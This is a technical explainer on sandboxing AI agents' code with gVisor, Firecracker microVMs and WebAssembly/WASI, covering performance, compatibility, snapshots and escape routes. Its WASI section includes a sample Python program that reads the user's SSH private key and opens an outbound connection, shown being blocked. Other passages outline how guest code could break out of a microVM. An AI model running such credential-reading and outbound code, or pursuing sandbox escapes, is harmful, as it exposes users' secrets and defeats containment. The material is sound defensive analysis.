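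An attacker who controls the Sentry can use everything the Sentry can, including the shared folders and the virtual network card, without needing a second flaw. The gVisor project therefore advises operators to put different customers in different sandboxes.

Some attacks do not involve system calls. A guest can infer another program's data from processor timing, and gVisor generally can't prevent this, so the host needs its own protection in the kernel or hardware. A guest can also use up memory and processor time, and gVisor relies on the host's cgroups to limit this. If someone misconfigures or subverts the software that starts containers, the guest may run without gVisor.

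An operator can check for a missing sandbox before the agent starts work by running `dmesg`, which prints the kernel's log. Under gVisor, the Sentry generates a fake log that opens with "Starting gVisor..." and continues with jokes such as "Digging up root...". In an ordinary container, `dmesg` normally fails or shows the host's messages.

### Why calculation is cheap and system calls are dear

gVisor lets the guest's own instructions run directly on the processor. Its cost comes mainly from system calls. Let T be a program's running time in an ordinary container, n the number of system calls it makes, and c the average extra time gVisor needs for each. The slowdown is roughly

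extra time ÷ T = (n × c) ÷ T

If c were two microseconds, a program that calculates for ten seconds and makes 1,000 calls would take two milliseconds longer, or 0.02%. With five million calls, it would take ten seconds longer, doubling its running time. The real value of c varies with the platform and the call. The formula also leaves out *page faults*, which occur when a program first touches a piece of memory and which the Sentry has to handle.

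The extra time has two sources. gVisor's *Performance Guide* calls the delay from intercepting each system call and passing it through the Sentry a *structural cost*, which the design makes unavoidable. An *implementation cost* arises where the Sentry's code, such as its network stack, is less refined than Linux's, and developers can reduce it. Whether the structural cost matters depends on how often the application makes system calls, according to the account of Ant Group's use that gVisor (2021) published.

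The guide's tests fit this pattern. Programs that computed prime numbers and trained a small neural network ran at about the same speed as in an ordinary container. The database Redis, which mostly moves small pieces of data over the network, was much slower, though the relative slowdown shrank when each request involved more work. A web server that repeatedly sent one small file also ran slowly, because the Sentry's file system handled many of those requests one at a time.

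These tests used ptrace, the slowest platform, on a years-old version of Linux, so they are better evidence of which programs slow down than of how much. Other figures have similar problems. Edera, which sells a competing sandbox, cites a 2019 academic study that found system calls 2 to 11 times slower under gVisor, but it acknowledges that systrap has since improved interception. gVisor's *Releasing Systrap* (2023) again used Redis as a test because system calls dominate its running time.

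File benchmarks can also make gVisor look faster than it is. Junior (2026), in *Unable to reproduce gVisor Performance Guide fio results*, reported that a standard disk test ran five to six times faster under runsc than under runc. Junior didn't believe the result, and tried turning off the in-memory layer and directfs to find the cause. A sandbox that serves files from memory can appear faster than the disk it is supposed to be using, so operators should confirm what a benchmark measures.

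The filter around the Sentry also adds overhead. Developers can measure it by running the same benchmark with and without the filter (gVisor, 2024), although nobody should run gVisor without the filter in production.

gVisor should only slightly slow an agent that analyses a spreadsheet, because the work is mostly calculation. Operators should expect more delay when an agent installs packages, searches a repository or runs a test suite, because these tasks involve many small file operations. Since an agent also waits for the model between commands, even a noticeable slowdown in a short command may add little to the task's total time.

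gVisor also needs memory for each Sentry, in a mostly fixed amount plus some for every open file and connection. It doesn't reserve a block of memory for each guest in advance, as a virtual machine typically does, so a host can reclaim memory that an idle sandbox has released.

### Programs that do not work

Because no call passes through to the host, a Linux feature works only if the Sentry implements it. Li and colleagues counted 260 supported system calls in a release from early 2021. gVisor's developers deliberately leave out many specialised interfaces, such as those for particular devices and file systems.

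gVisor's own documents differ in how cautious they are. *Applications* warns that there "always will be" missing features and bugs, and that trying a program is the only real way to know whether it works. The project's page on application compatibility, by gVisor, says that problems are rare and lists Claude Code, OpenClaw and Hermes among the programs that work. The list is a best-effort one, and a program on it may still have faults. For an agent, a tested harness is only a start, since the model can install a package that nobody has tested.

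In September 2026 the developers added support for *systemd*, the program that starts and manages services on most Linux systems, along with several kernel features it needs. A container can now run something close to a whole Linux system, including a graphical desktop. Edera lists one major gap: gVisor doesn't run *eBPF* programs, small programs that administrators load into a kernel to monitor it. Tools that monitor ordinary containers from the host therefore detect little of what happens inside a gVisor guest. Edera's page may predate the September additions, so operators who rely on such tools should test the current release.

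### GPUs

A program that uses a GPU has to communicate with the manufacturer's driver, a large piece of software that runs partly in the host's kernel. The Sentry has no replacement for this driver, so GPU work exposes the guest to complex host code that gVisor otherwise keeps it away from, and a flaw in the driver could let the guest bypass the Sentry. In a marketing comparison, Edera marks gVisor as lacking both GPU driver isolation and support for GPUs from several manufacturers. Edera has a commercial interest in that comparison, but its point about the driver follows from gVisor's design.

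Most code interpreters don't need a GPU, because the language model runs elsewhere and the sandbox only executes its programs. Operators can avoid the problem by leaving the GPU out, unless their service lets agents train or run models inside the sandbox.

### Saving and restoring a sandbox

gVisor can save a running sandbox to files and restore it later, on the same machine or another. The saved state, a *snapshot*, includes every process, open file and network socket and all of the guest's memory. Because the Sentry already keeps the guest's kernel records, it can write them out without involving the host's kernel in each one.

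gVisor's *The Sandbox Kernel for Agents* suggests several uses. A service can load Python and its libraries once, save the result and start later sandboxes from it. It can store an idle user's session and free the memory, or copy a session so that an agent can try two approaches from the same point. A snapshot also contains any password or access token that was in the guest's memory, so whoever stores it has to protect it accordingly.

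In a test published on the gVisor blog in November 2026, restoring a sandbox with 2 gibibytes of memory from a slow disk took 939 milliseconds, compared with 5,106 in earlier versions. When the host already held the files in memory, the time fell from 651 milliseconds to 71. Some of the gain comes from leaving snapshots uncompressed. Ranjan (2026) found in *Changing runsc checkpoint compression default* that compression saved little space and prevented gVisor from restoring the kernel's state and the guest's memory at the same time.

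Part of a restore takes the same time whatever the size of the sandbox. In a March 2026 proposal in gVisor's *runsc* repository, a contributor put the time to start a new Sentry, install its filters and prepare the platform at about 80 milliseconds. That is more than the 71 milliseconds the blog later gave for a whole restore, so the two tests must have differed in hardware or in what they timed. The contributor proposed keeping a prepared Sentry ready, which would help services that restore the same snapshot hundreds of times.

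gVisor can start restoring a program before all of its memory has arrived. Modal (2025), which runs customers' code in the cloud, reports that gVisor loads the rest in the background while the program runs. If the program needs a page that hasn't been loaded, it waits, and fetching one over the network takes tens of milliseconds. Modal loads the memory file early to make these waits rare, and reported starts about 2.5 times faster.

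GPU programs are harder to save because some of their state is on the graphics card. *Reducing GPU Cold Starts with Memory Snapshots* describes how Cerebrium, a hosting company, restores them using a modified version of the component that starts gVisor containers and its own service on every host to move and store the snapshots. The company found the order of events at startup the hardest part. An operator can't assume that an unmodified gVisor installation will restore GPU programs in the same way.

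### Tencent's agent-training sandboxes

The largest published test of gVisor's compatibility with agents' work comes from the Chinese technology company Tencent. *Scaling Agentic-RL Sandboxes to the Millions with gVisor at Tencent* (Tan, Liu and Chen, 2026) reports that the company runs millions of gVisor sandboxes a day to train agents by reinforcement learning, which rewards a model for completing tasks. Most of the tasks are programming problems from real software projects. If a correct solution failed because of an incompatibility with gVisor, the training would treat it as wrong.

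Tencent chose gVisor because it separates the guest from the host's kernel and works with the company's existing container systems. gVisor also runs inside ordinary virtual machines. Tencent's engineers say microVMs need physical servers, which would cost more.

Each test case ran under both runc and gVisor to expose incompatibilities, and the logs were kept. Software then filtered out differences unrelated to the sandbox and sent AI agents the cases that failed only under gVisor. The agents read the logs and source code, proposed a cause for each failure and classified it as a gVisor flaw, a timing problem, an environment difference or a faulty test. Engineers reviewed the proposed explanations and fixes. The agents examined thousands of cases, and the engineers studied more than 100 in depth.

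The comparison covered 74,379 cases from ten collections. The table gives the share that passed in six of them and overall.

| Collection | Cases | runc | gVisor before fixes | gVisor after fixes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| terminal-bench2 | 89 | 100.00% | 94.38% | 97.75% |
| Multi-SWE-bench | 1,632 | 70.16% | 72.49% | 73.16% |
| Multi-SWE-RL | 7,046 | 27.73% | 20.49% | 26.81% |
| SWE-bench Verified | 500 | 100.00% | 99.60% | 100.00% |
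| SWE-rebench | 21,336 | 83.33% | 83.33% | 83.77% |
| SWE-smith | 38,513 | 99.37% | 97.42% | 99.31% |
| All ten | 74,379 | 86.78% | 85.18% | 86.91% |

About 13% of cases failed even under runc, so a team that tested only gVisor could easily have blamed gVisor for those failures. Tencent's testing framework also handled Multi-SWE-RL badly under both systems. The fixes raised gVisor's overall pass rate by 1.7 percentage points. Many failures came from a few projects, where one repair could resolve hundreds of cases.

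Tan and colleagues conclude that replacing runc with gVisor reduces correctness very little. The overall rates support this, but differences between collections cancel out in them. After the fixes, gVisor passed roughly 90 fewer cases than runc in three collections and roughly 185 more in four others. gVisor has no obvious way to make programs more correct, so the extra passes probably come from tests whose results vary between runs. The same randomness may also mask real failures. On terminal-bench2, a small collection of command-line tasks, two of the 89 cases still failed only under gVisor.

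Some of the causes were bugs in the Sentry. When the terminal program tmux checked its connections for activity, the Sentry changed part of the request that Linux leaves alone. tmux then repeated the request endlessly, using 96.6% of a processor core. After the fix, it used almost none. Another project failed because gVisor lacked a system call for copying part of a file and didn't notify programs when another program emptied a file they were watching. Other programs looked for small system files that the Sentry didn't provide.

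Some failures under gVisor came from timing or test order rather than from gVisor itself. One Android project's build deleted a folder while another step was still writing to it. The build also failed in five of seven runs under runc, but gVisor's slower system calls made the collision more likely. The engineers fixed it by running the two steps separately. A test from the website builder Jekyll failed about a third of the time in any environment, depending on the random order in which the tests ran, and it happened to fail under gVisor.

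More than ten of the resulting fixes are now in the main version of gVisor, so other operators get them too. These fixes cover files, networking, system information and the terminal features that interactive agents use. For the remaining cases, the engineers recommend changing the workload, such as by downloading Java packages in advance and running fewer build steps at once.

The study measured whether programs gave the right result, but not how long they took or whether the sandbox would withstand an attack. It also left out GPU workloads. Tencent's engineers wrote it for gVisor's blog after committing to the product, but any operator can repeat the method by running a sample of the agent's real tasks under both runtimes before switching.

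## Firecracker: a small virtual machine per sandbox

gVisor replaces Linux with a substitute, so a program can fail wherever the two differ. A *microVM* gives each guest a real Linux kernel of its own and relies on the processor to keep that kernel away from the host. It is a virtual machine with very few virtual devices, built to start fast. Firecracker, a program that runs microVMs, comes from Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud business. AWS wrote it for Lambda, which runs customers' short programs on demand, and published the code in 2018.

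Lambda originally ran each program in a container and gave every customer separate virtual machines. According to *Firecracker* (Agache, Brooker and colleagues, 2020), Lambda abandoned this design because containers forced a choice between blocking system calls and exposing the host's kernel, and because virtual machines of a fixed size were hard to fill efficiently.

### How the processor separates guest and host

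A processor has a restricted mode for programs and a privileged mode for the kernel. Hardware virtualisation also separates host from guest, and each has both modes. The guest's kernel has full kernel privileges, but only inside the guest.

A kernel keeps *page tables*, which translate the addresses a program uses into locations in the machine's memory. When a guest is running, the processor translates the result a second time, using tables that the host controls. The guest's kernel can change its own tables in any way, but its addresses still lead only to memory that the host has assigned to it.

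Most of the guest's instructions run directly on the processor, and its own kernel handles its system calls without involving the host. If the guest tries to use a device, the processor stops it and switches to the host's kernel. This is called a *VM exit*. KVM, which is part of that kernel, handles some exits itself, for instance by supplying memory that the guest is using for the first time. It passes device requests to the *virtual machine monitor*, an ordinary program on the host.

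Firecracker is such a monitor. Each microVM has its own Firecracker process, with one thread per virtual processor and another for management, according to an early account on the Linux news site LWN.

This changes which programs run slowly. gVisor adds time to every system call. In a microVM, system calls take about as long as usual, and the extra time comes from exits, mainly for disk and network traffic.

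### One disk write

Suppose the guest's Python runs this line:

`open("total.txt", "w").write("42")`

Python makes its usual system calls. The guest's kernel creates the file in its own file system, stores the two characters in the guest's memory and lets Python continue. The host has not done anything yet.

Later, the guest's kernel saves the data to its disk, which is a *virtual device*, meaning software that behaves like hardware. Firecracker's disk and network card follow *virtio*, an open standard for such devices. The guest's disk driver queues a request in the guest's memory, giving the position on the disk, the length, and the data's address in memory. The driver then writes to a special address to notify the disk.

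Since no real disk exists at that address, the processor stops the guest, and KVM notifies the Firecracker process. Firecracker can read the guest's memory, so it takes the request from the queue, delaying it if the guest has used up its allowance of disk operations. Firecracker then makes an ordinary system call on the host to write the data into a single file that holds the guest's entire disk. The host's kernel saves that file like any other. Firecracker marks the request as complete, and KVM signals the guest's kernel.

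The host receives a position in the disk file, not the name `total.txt`. Agache and colleagues chose this arrangement for security, because file systems are large and complex, and a guest that could request individual files would reach much more of the host's kernel. Unlike gVisor, Firecracker can't share a project folder directly, so the agent's harness has to copy the project into the guest and copy the results out.

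Network traffic follows a similar route. The guest's kernel opens the connection and builds the packets, and Firecracker passes them to a virtual network interface on the host. Firecracker can limit the rate of traffic, but the operator decides where the traffic may go.

### Few devices and a confined monitor

Each virtual device is host code that the guest can reach, so a flaw in one could give the guest control of the monitor. QEMU, a general-purpose monitor, supports more than 40 devices and had over 1.4 million lines of code in 2020. Firecracker had about 50,000 lines and provided a disk, a network card, a serial port and part of a keyboard controller. The keyboard controller code took fewer than 50 lines.

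AWS built Firecracker from crosvm, Google's virtual machine monitor for Chrome OS, and removed what Lambda didn't need, including the USB and GPU drivers. Firecracker has since gained a few features. Its January 2026 README lists virtual devices for random numbers and persistent memory, and a way to add memory to a running guest.

Firecracker's developers wrote it in Rust, which, like Go, prevents most memory errors. They left tasks such as sharing processor time among guests and managing memory to the host's kernel, so administrators can list or stop microVMs with the usual Linux commands. Agache and colleagues acknowledge that this makes Firecracker's security depend on more of the host's kernel.

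A separate program, the *jailer*, confines the monitor before the guest starts, using the same mechanisms as a process sandbox. The monitor gets a private file tree containing little besides Firecracker and the guest's disk, separate process and network namespaces, and an account without special privileges. In 2020 the monitor's seccomp filter permitted 24 system calls, far fewer than Docker's default, and checked their arguments. It also permitted 30 kinds of device command, 22 of them for KVM.

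The filter can be this strict because, like gVisor's, it applies to a program with a fixed job. Firecracker now has a separate filter for each type of thread, so a thread that runs a virtual processor isn't also allowed to make the system calls that the management thread needs.

### What an escape would require

Agache and colleagues treat all code in a microVM as untrusted, including the guest kernel. An interpreter running as root already has much of that kernel's power.

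One way for a guest to escape is through the monitor. It would need a flaw in a virtual device to run its own code in the Firecracker process, then a second flaw to get past the jailer's restrictions. The second flaw would probably have to be in the small part of the host's kernel that the filter leaves exposed. An operator who starts Firecracker without the jailer removes much of this second barrier.

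An attacker has a shorter route to the host through KVM because KVM is part of the host's kernel. A flaw in its code for handling exits could give the guest direct control of the host, and the jailer would not help. KVM had about 120,000 lines of code in 2020, far fewer than Linux as a whole but more than Firecracker, so counting only Firecracker's lines understates the attack surface.

As with gVisor, the host needs its own protection against attacks that use processor timing. Agache and colleagues recommend several precautions, including turning off the feature that lets two threads share a processor core. AWS applies them in Lambda, but Firecracker doesn't apply them itself, so other operators must.

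### Start-up time and memory use

The 2020 paper is the usual source for Firecracker's performance figures. Firecracker's current specification sets limits for a guest with two virtual processors and 256 MiB of memory, running a kernel tuned for Firecracker.

| Measure | 2020 paper | Current specification |
|---|---|---|
| Monitor's memory for each microVM | about 3 MB | at most 5 MiB |
| Guest start, up to its first program | under 125 ms with a minimal kernel; from 150 ms with a production setup | at most 125 ms |
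| Starting the Firecracker process | no separate figure | typically about 12 ms, at most 60 ms |

LWN's early account gives nearly the same limits and says that automated tests enforce them. Because these are upper limits, Firecracker may have become faster even though they have barely changed.

Agache and colleagues compared three monitors on the same server. QEMU took about twice as long to start a guest as a preconfigured Firecracker process. Cloud Hypervisor, another Rust monitor, was slightly faster than Firecracker when guests started one at a time. When 50 started at once, 99% of Firecracker guests were ready within 146 milliseconds, compared with 158 milliseconds for Cloud Hypervisor.

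The monitor's memory overhead was about 3 MB for Firecracker, 13 MB for Cloud Hypervisor and 131 MB for QEMU. This difference was decisive for Lambda, because its smallest functions use 128 MB and QEMU would have doubled their memory use. Agent sandboxes are often much larger. QEMU's overhead would be about 1.5% in a guest the size of the 9 GB container that Willison examined. These figures exclude the memory that each microVM's guest kernel needs.

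In 2020 Firecracker was slow at moving data. It handled disk requests one at a time, so a guest could make about 13,000 small reads a second on hardware capable of more than 340,000. Network traffic reached about 15 gigabits a second, compared with 44 on the host. AWS expected to improve both, so operators should measure the current version before relying on these numbers.

### What the user waits for

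The 125 milliseconds in the specification run from when a configured Firecracker process receives the start command to when the guest's kernel starts its first program. A user who asks an agent to analyse a spreadsheet also waits for the service to choose a host and, if the guest's disk image isn't already there, fetch it over the network. After the kernel starts, the guest still has to start Python, load the libraries and connect to the harness. Fetching a large image or loading a slow library can easily take longer than starting the virtual machine.

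The choice of guest kernel also affects boot time. The standard Ubuntu kernel added 900 milliseconds in AWS's tests, partly because it searched for old devices that Firecracker doesn't provide. A network card added about 20 milliseconds, and decompressing the kernel added about 40.

Firecracker virtual machines still start much faster than conventional ones. In jvns.ca's *Firecracker* (2021), a programmer who wanted to give each visitor to a puzzle website a virtual machine found that a rented cloud machine took about a minute to start, QEMU took at least 20 seconds, and Firecracker took less than one second.

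Lambda hides the remaining delay by keeping a few microVMs running in advance. Agache and colleagues calculate how many it needs from a rule in queueing theory, Little's law:

average pool size = new sandboxes per second × seconds to prepare each one

With a preparation time of 125 milliseconds, a service that starts 40 sandboxes a second needs five in reserve. If loading Python and its libraries raises that time to three seconds, the service needs 120, all of which use memory while they wait. A harness that serves one user can avoid most of the delay by starting the sandbox while the model is still writing its first program.

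### Snapshots and copy-on-write

As with gVisor, a service can avoid repeating the preparation by restoring a snapshot. An older edition of Firecracker's snapshot guide explains the process.

The operator starts one microVM, loads Python and the libraries into it, and pauses it. Firecracker then writes the guest's memory to one file and the state of its virtual processors and devices to another. The operator copies the disk separately.

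To restore the sandbox, the operator starts a new Firecracker process and gives it both files. Firecracker reads the small state file and *maps* the memory file, meaning the host's kernel connects the guest's memory to the file without loading it. The guest then resumes at the instruction where it paused, and the host loads each piece of memory from the file when the guest first reads it.

When the guest writes to a piece of memory, the host gives it a private copy of that piece and leaves the file unchanged. This technique, *copy-on-write*, lets many guests share one file. Suppose a snapshot holds 512 MiB and each restored guest changes 40 MiB. Twenty guests then need at most 512 + 20 × 40 = 1,312 MiB, compared with 10,240 MiB if each had a full copy.

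*Restoring Uniqueness in MicroVM Snapshots* (2021), by AWS researchers, reports restores in as little as 4 milliseconds. That figure doesn't include loading the memory the guest is about to use, which causes waits like those Modal reduced under gVisor. *FaaSnap* describes a system that records which parts of the snapshot a program needs and loads them early. The system ran programs up to 3.5 times faster than REAP, an earlier method, and on average 3.5% slower than when the whole snapshot was already in memory.

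The operator has to keep the memory file unchanged while any restored guest is running, because a change would corrupt every one of them. Firecracker treats snapshot files as trusted, and its checksum on the state file detects only accidental damage, so the operator must protect the files against tampering. Open network connections may not survive a restore, and the guest's clock continues from the moment of the snapshot until something corrects it. Sharing the memory file also conflicts with one of AWS's precautions from 2020, which was to avoid sharing files between guests because a guest can sometimes tell from timing what another has read. A cautious service could keep a separate copy of the file for each customer.

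In June 2026, AWS's *Run isolated sandboxes with full lifecycle control* introduced Lambda MicroVMs, a product for agents built around snapshots. The customer supplies a description of a container image, and AWS builds the image, starts the application and takes a snapshot from which every later sandbox resumes. The service can also suspend an idle sandbox and restore it, with its files and running programs, when the user returns. A sandbox can run for up to eight hours in total, with up to 16 virtual processors and 32 GB of memory. AWS describes launching a sandbox as "near-instant" but gives no times.

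### Clones that share random numbers and secrets

Guests restored from the same snapshot are *clones* that begin with identical memory, so anything that has to be unique may be duplicated across them.

Random numbers are the main example. Software usually calculates them from an internal state, and two generators with the same state produce the same numbers. If a service loads Python's `random` module before taking its snapshot, every clone will draw the same first number from it. This does little harm when a program is shuffling a list, but if it is creating passwords, a user with another clone could generate the same ones.

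According to Firecracker's older guide, resuming the same state more than once is insecure unless something guarantees that unique values stay unique. This includes restoring a snapshot once while the original microVM keeps running. The guide's safe pattern is to stop the original and restore the snapshot once. This suits a service that suspends a single user's session, but not one that starts thousands of sandboxes from one prepared state.

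Part of the solution is a virtual device that gives the guest a random 128-bit identifier, which changes after each restore. The UAPI Group's *UAPI.14 VMGenID* specifies the device. Firecracker added it in 2024, and Linux has used it since version 5.18 to refresh the kernel's own random-number generator.

However, the kernel can't refresh random number generators inside other programs. Chalios (2022), an AWS engineer, pointed out that these generators and any stored identifiers stay identical after cloning. AWS's *#SnapSafety* (2024) also describes the device's signal as "slightly racy". A program may draw a number before the guest's kernel responds to the notification.

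Firecracker's *Entropy for Clones* says there is no general solution for programs with their own random number generators, and recommends not using those generators before the snapshot. It also advises operators to delete any file in which the guest has saved random data for its next start. For Lambda MicroVMs, AWS's *Working with snapshots* tells developers to create identifiers and secrets only after a sandbox starts, and to use generators that draw on the kernel, such as Python's `secrets` module. Programs that use the encryption library OpenSSL need AWS's modified version.

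Operators can't count on a model to follow this advice in the code it writes, so it is safer for the service to reset the random number generators in Python and its libraries after each restore, before it runs any of the model's code.

Any password or access token in a snapshot is also in every clone. The right time to take a shared snapshot is after the libraries have loaded and before any customer's data arrives. gVisor snapshots carry the same risks, because a Python process that the Sentry restores twice resumes with identical memory each time.

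### Hosts, memory, GPUs and guest kernels

Firecracker requires a Linux host with KVM. AWS's *Announcing the Firecracker Open Source Technology* told users in 2018 to run it on a physical server and give it access to KVM's device file. Many companies instead rent virtual machines, where Firecracker works only if the provider allows *nested virtualisation*, in which one virtual machine runs inside another. The extra layer also makes exits slower. A managed service such as Lambda MicroVMs avoids the problem because the provider runs the hosts.

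A microVM has a fixed memory limit, but the host supplies memory only as the guest uses it, so an operator can promise guests more memory than the server has. AWS reported ratios of up to ten to one in production, which work because unrelated customers seldom need their full allowance at the same time. Agents that all run the same job at once would need their memory together. A guest's kernel also tends to keep freed memory as a file cache, so idle sandboxes can hold more than they need.

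Firecracker does not give guests a GPU. Its developers left out direct hardware access because servers in 2020 couldn't divide a device among thousands of short-lived guests. AWS's 2026 announcement of Lambda MicroVMs lists processors, memory and disk, but still no GPU option. An operator whose agents train models inside the sandbox needs a virtual machine monitor that can assign a physical GPU to a guest.

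Compatibility is otherwise good. Agache and colleagues found no software that failed in a microVM, except programs that needed particular hardware. When AWS moved Lambda's customers to Firecracker, the changed timing exposed a few existing bugs in AWS's own development kit and another library. Firecracker can't run Windows guests without significant changes.

The operator must keep each guest's kernel up to date. AWS replaces a host's entire software image when it needs a patch, and in 2020 it recycled every Lambda sandbox within 12 hours. Snapshots make patching easier to forget, because a guest restored from one keeps running the old kernel. To update it, the operator has to start a new guest with the patched kernel and take another snapshot. An unpatched guest kernel doesn't by itself give an attacker access to the host, but it can let an ordinary program in the guest become root and remove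 any restrictions the operator placed there.

### Kata Containers, Cloud Hypervisor and libkrun

Firecracker runs virtual machines but doesn't handle container images or manage groups of machines. Kata Containers provides some of what is missing by letting ordinary container tools start each workload in a virtual machine, with a choice of virtual machine monitors. Northflank, which sells sandboxes, uses Kata mainly with Cloud Hypervisor, which shares much of its code with Firecracker but also supports Windows guests and Microsoft's hypervisor. Azure's sandboxes for agent code use Microsoft's own Hyper-V, according to InfoQ (2026). For a single developer on Linux, libkrun may be simpler, because Podman, a container program, can use it to run a container as a microVM with one extra option. Fedora Magazine shows how to run Claude Code this way. Its guide reports start-up in hundreds of milliseconds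 but warns that the default memory is too small and that the guest starts as root even if the image names another user. It also warns that a microVM "is not a bulletproof boundary" and recommends a full virtual machine or a cloud machine for software that might be dangerous.

### SideKernel: microVMs for coding agents on macOS

KVM is part of Linux, so a developer with a Mac needs another way to run microVMs. *SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026) presents an open-source sandbox that uses Apple's Virtualization framework to run Claude Code in a microVM. The guest uses a small Linux kernel from the Kata project and an Ubuntu file system.

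Prasakis first surveyed developers to find out why they avoid sandboxes. Of 68 respondents who used coding agents, 26 ran them in a sandbox, 7 had stopped, and 35 had never done so. Among the 35 who had never used a sandbox, 21 had never considered it and 9 thought the benefit wasn't worth the effort. Current and former users complained most about networking, setting up the environment again, and sharing files. Prasakis recruited respondents through his own contacts, a startup community and a Georgia Tech course, and treats the answers as informal. A third of the respondents worked in security, so sandbox use among developers in general may be lower.

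SideKernel removes these obstacles at some risk. When a developer starts it, the current project folder appears in the guest, and changes made there affect the real files. Firecracker's designers rejected this kind of file sharing. The agent can delete the project, but the developer's private key is not in the guest unless it is inside that folder. She can bring in other files one at a time by approving a prompt on the Mac. SideKernel also makes any network port the guest opens available on the Mac, which helps with testing a website but could expose her to a malicious service.

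Claude's login stays on the Mac, where a small program adds it to the agent's requests. Outbound network access is either fully open or limited to Anthropic's service, so a developer who needs to install one package must give the agent access to the whole internet.

Prasakis then compared SideKernel with four similar products in 23 tests. Each test checked whether a product had a documented, built-in way to do a task, such as copying an image into the sandbox or keeping installed packages after a restart. SideKernel and Docker Sandboxes, Docker's microVM product, both passed 19. Microsandbox, SmolVM and Shuru each passed 12. SideKernel did better at sharing files, while Docker Sandboxes was the only product to pass all five network tests.

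Prasakis built SideKernel, wrote the tests and scored them, and the tests came from the same survey that shaped SideKernel's features. Its high score is therefore unsurprising, and Docker's equal score is probably more informative. The tests count features without measuring how easy they are for developers to use, and none involved attacking a sandbox. The argument that SideKernel is secure therefore depends on its design, particularly the separate kernel, and on the choices a developer makes about its shared folder and network.

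## WebAssembly and WASI: no access unless granted

Process sandboxes, gVisor and Firecracker run ordinary programs and limit what they can reach, whereas WebAssembly (*Wasm*) limits the instructions a program can contain. Browser makers designed this portable instruction format so that web pages could run compiled code from strangers. A compiler translates C, Rust or another language into a Wasm *module*, and a *runtime* translates the module into machine code. Wasm has no instruction for making a system call. A module can calculate and change its own memory, but for anything else it needs functions that the surrounding software supplies.

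### Memory, jumps and calls

A module keeps its data in *linear memory*, an array of bytes numbered from zero. A pointer in a C program becomes a position in this array, so the module never handles a real address in the host's memory. Suppose the array has n bytes and an instruction reads w bytes starting at position p. The runtime allows the read only if

p + w ≤ n

Linear memory grows in units of 65,536 bytes. If a module has one unit and tries to read four bytes at position 65,534, the read would extend to 65,538, past the end of memory, so the module *traps* (stops with an error). Most modules use 32-bit positions and can address at most 4 GiB, which may be too little for an agent that loads a large dataset.

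Comparing two numbers before every access would slow programs down, so Wasmtime, the Bytecode Alliance's runtime for use outside browsers, normally leaves the check to the processor. According to Wasmtime's *Security*, by default it relies on page faults, which interrupt the program when it touches an address with no usable memory behind it. Wasmtime also leaves an empty 2 GiB region before the array in case its compiler has a bug. If faulty machine code treated a 32-bit position as a signed number, the position could be as low as −2³¹, or 2 GiB before the start of the array, and the access would still land in the empty region.

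Wasm also restricts which instruction can run next. A native program keeps each function's return address in memory that the program can write to, and attackers have long exploited this by overwriting the address. A Wasm runtime keeps return addresses outside linear memory, where the module can't access them. A jump can only go to a valid place in the same function. When a program chooses at run time which function to call, the runtime checks that the choice is a real function with the expected argument types.

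These rules protect the host from the module, but a bug in the module can still corrupt the module's own data. According to WebAssembly's security page, compilers place some C variables in linear memory, such as those whose address the program uses. Writing past the end of one can overwrite the program's other data. A service that processed two customers' files in the same running copy of a module, called an *instance*, could therefore mix up their data, whereas separate instances have separate memories.

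### Authority that starts from nothing

The software that runs a module is its *embedder*, which may be a browser, a server or an agent's harness. The core Wasm specification does not define how programs interact with their surroundings, and W3C's *WebAssembly JavaScript Interface* explains that the embedder makes that connection. The embedder does this mainly through *imports*, which are functions that the module names and the embedder supplies when it starts the module.

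Suppose the embedder supplies functions f₁ to fₙ. Apart from the processor time and memory it uses, the module's authority P is then the union of their effects, plus whatever they can do in combination:

P = E(f₁) ∪ E(f₂) ∪ … ∪ E(fₙ)

With no imports, P is empty. The import list therefore limits a program the way a tool allowlist limits an agent whose tools are all narrow. It also fails in the same way if the embedder supplies a function that runs any shell command on the host, because P then includes everything that command's process is permitted to do.

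WASI, the WebAssembly System Interface, is a standard set of imports for files, network connections, clocks, random numbers and similar resources. WASI's *Security* contrasts it with Linux and Windows, where a process inherits its user's broad permissions unless somebody adds a sandbox. A WASI program can open only the folders its embedder grants, so if the embedder forgets one, the program fails and the operator finds out. In a process sandbox, programs can read any folder the builder forgets to hide, and nobody may notice.

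WASI's developers also call this stronger than typical process isolation, because the limits apply regardless of what the host process is allowed to do. The claim is fair for the defaults, but it assumes that the runtime enforces them without error.

### One directory and three requests

Suppose a harness runs Python as a WASI 0.1 module, using the oldest version of the interface still in wide use. It grants the module one directory, the developer's project folder, under the name `/project`. The model writes this program:

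```python
notes = open("/project/notes.txt").read()
key = open("/home/dev/.ssh/id_ed25519").read()

import socket
socket.create_connection(("192.0.2.10", 443))
```

Before the program starts, the runtime opens the folder, now called a *preopened directory*, and gives the module a numbered handle for it. The handle is usually 3, since 0 to 2 are for input, output and error messages. It is a *capability* because it both identifies the folder and grants the right to use it.

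For the first line, the C library inside the module compares the path with the names of its preopened directories and finds `/project`. It calls the import `path_open` with handle 3 and the rest of the path, `notes.txt`. The runtime looks up that name in the real folder, makes a system call to open the file, and returns a new handle. The module passes the new handle to another import, `fd_read`, which copies the file's contents into linear memory.

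No preopened directory covers the path in the second line, so the C library normally reports that the file doesn't exist, without calling the host. A program could bypass the library and call `path_open` itself, but each call needs a directory handle, and the module has a handle for only one directory. The runtime also rejects relative paths and symbolic links that lead out of that directory.

The last line fails because WASI 0.1 has no function for opening a new connection. A module can use a network socket only if the runtime has already given it one.

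| Request | Ordinary process under the developer's account | WASI 0.1 module | WASI 0.2 or 0.3 component |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read `/project/notes.txt` | succeeds | succeeds | succeeds |
| Read the private key | succeeds | fails, no handle covers it | fails, no handle covers it |
| Open the connection | succeeds | fails, no such function | fails, unless the host grants network access |

Later versions of WASI do have functions for opening connections, and a program that uses them declares them as imports. The embedder can leave them out, in which case a program that requires them won't start, or supply versions that refuse every address.

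The granted folder is the developer's real one, so a program with write access can delete the project. Embedders can instead grant read-only access or a copy of the folder.

### Components and WASI's versions

A plain Wasm module exchanges only numbers with its embedder. To pass text, both sides have to agree on where it sits in linear memory and how to encode it. The *component model*, a further specification, standardizes this by wrapping modules into *components*, whose interfaces can use text, lists and records. Developers describe these interfaces in a language called WIT. Each component keeps its own memory, and a component written in Rust can call one written in Go.

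A component's file lists its imports, so an operator can see what kinds of access it requires before running it. The list is less informative for an interpreter, because a Python component has to import whatever any Python program might need, regardless of what the program the model has just written uses.

Language libraries also tend to import more than a program uses. The Bytecode Alliance's *The Road to Component Model 1.0* (2026) describes a planned remedy, *optional imports*, which would let a component run even if the embedder does not supply a particular resource.

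WASI's *Releases* gives the status of the three versions as of November 2026.

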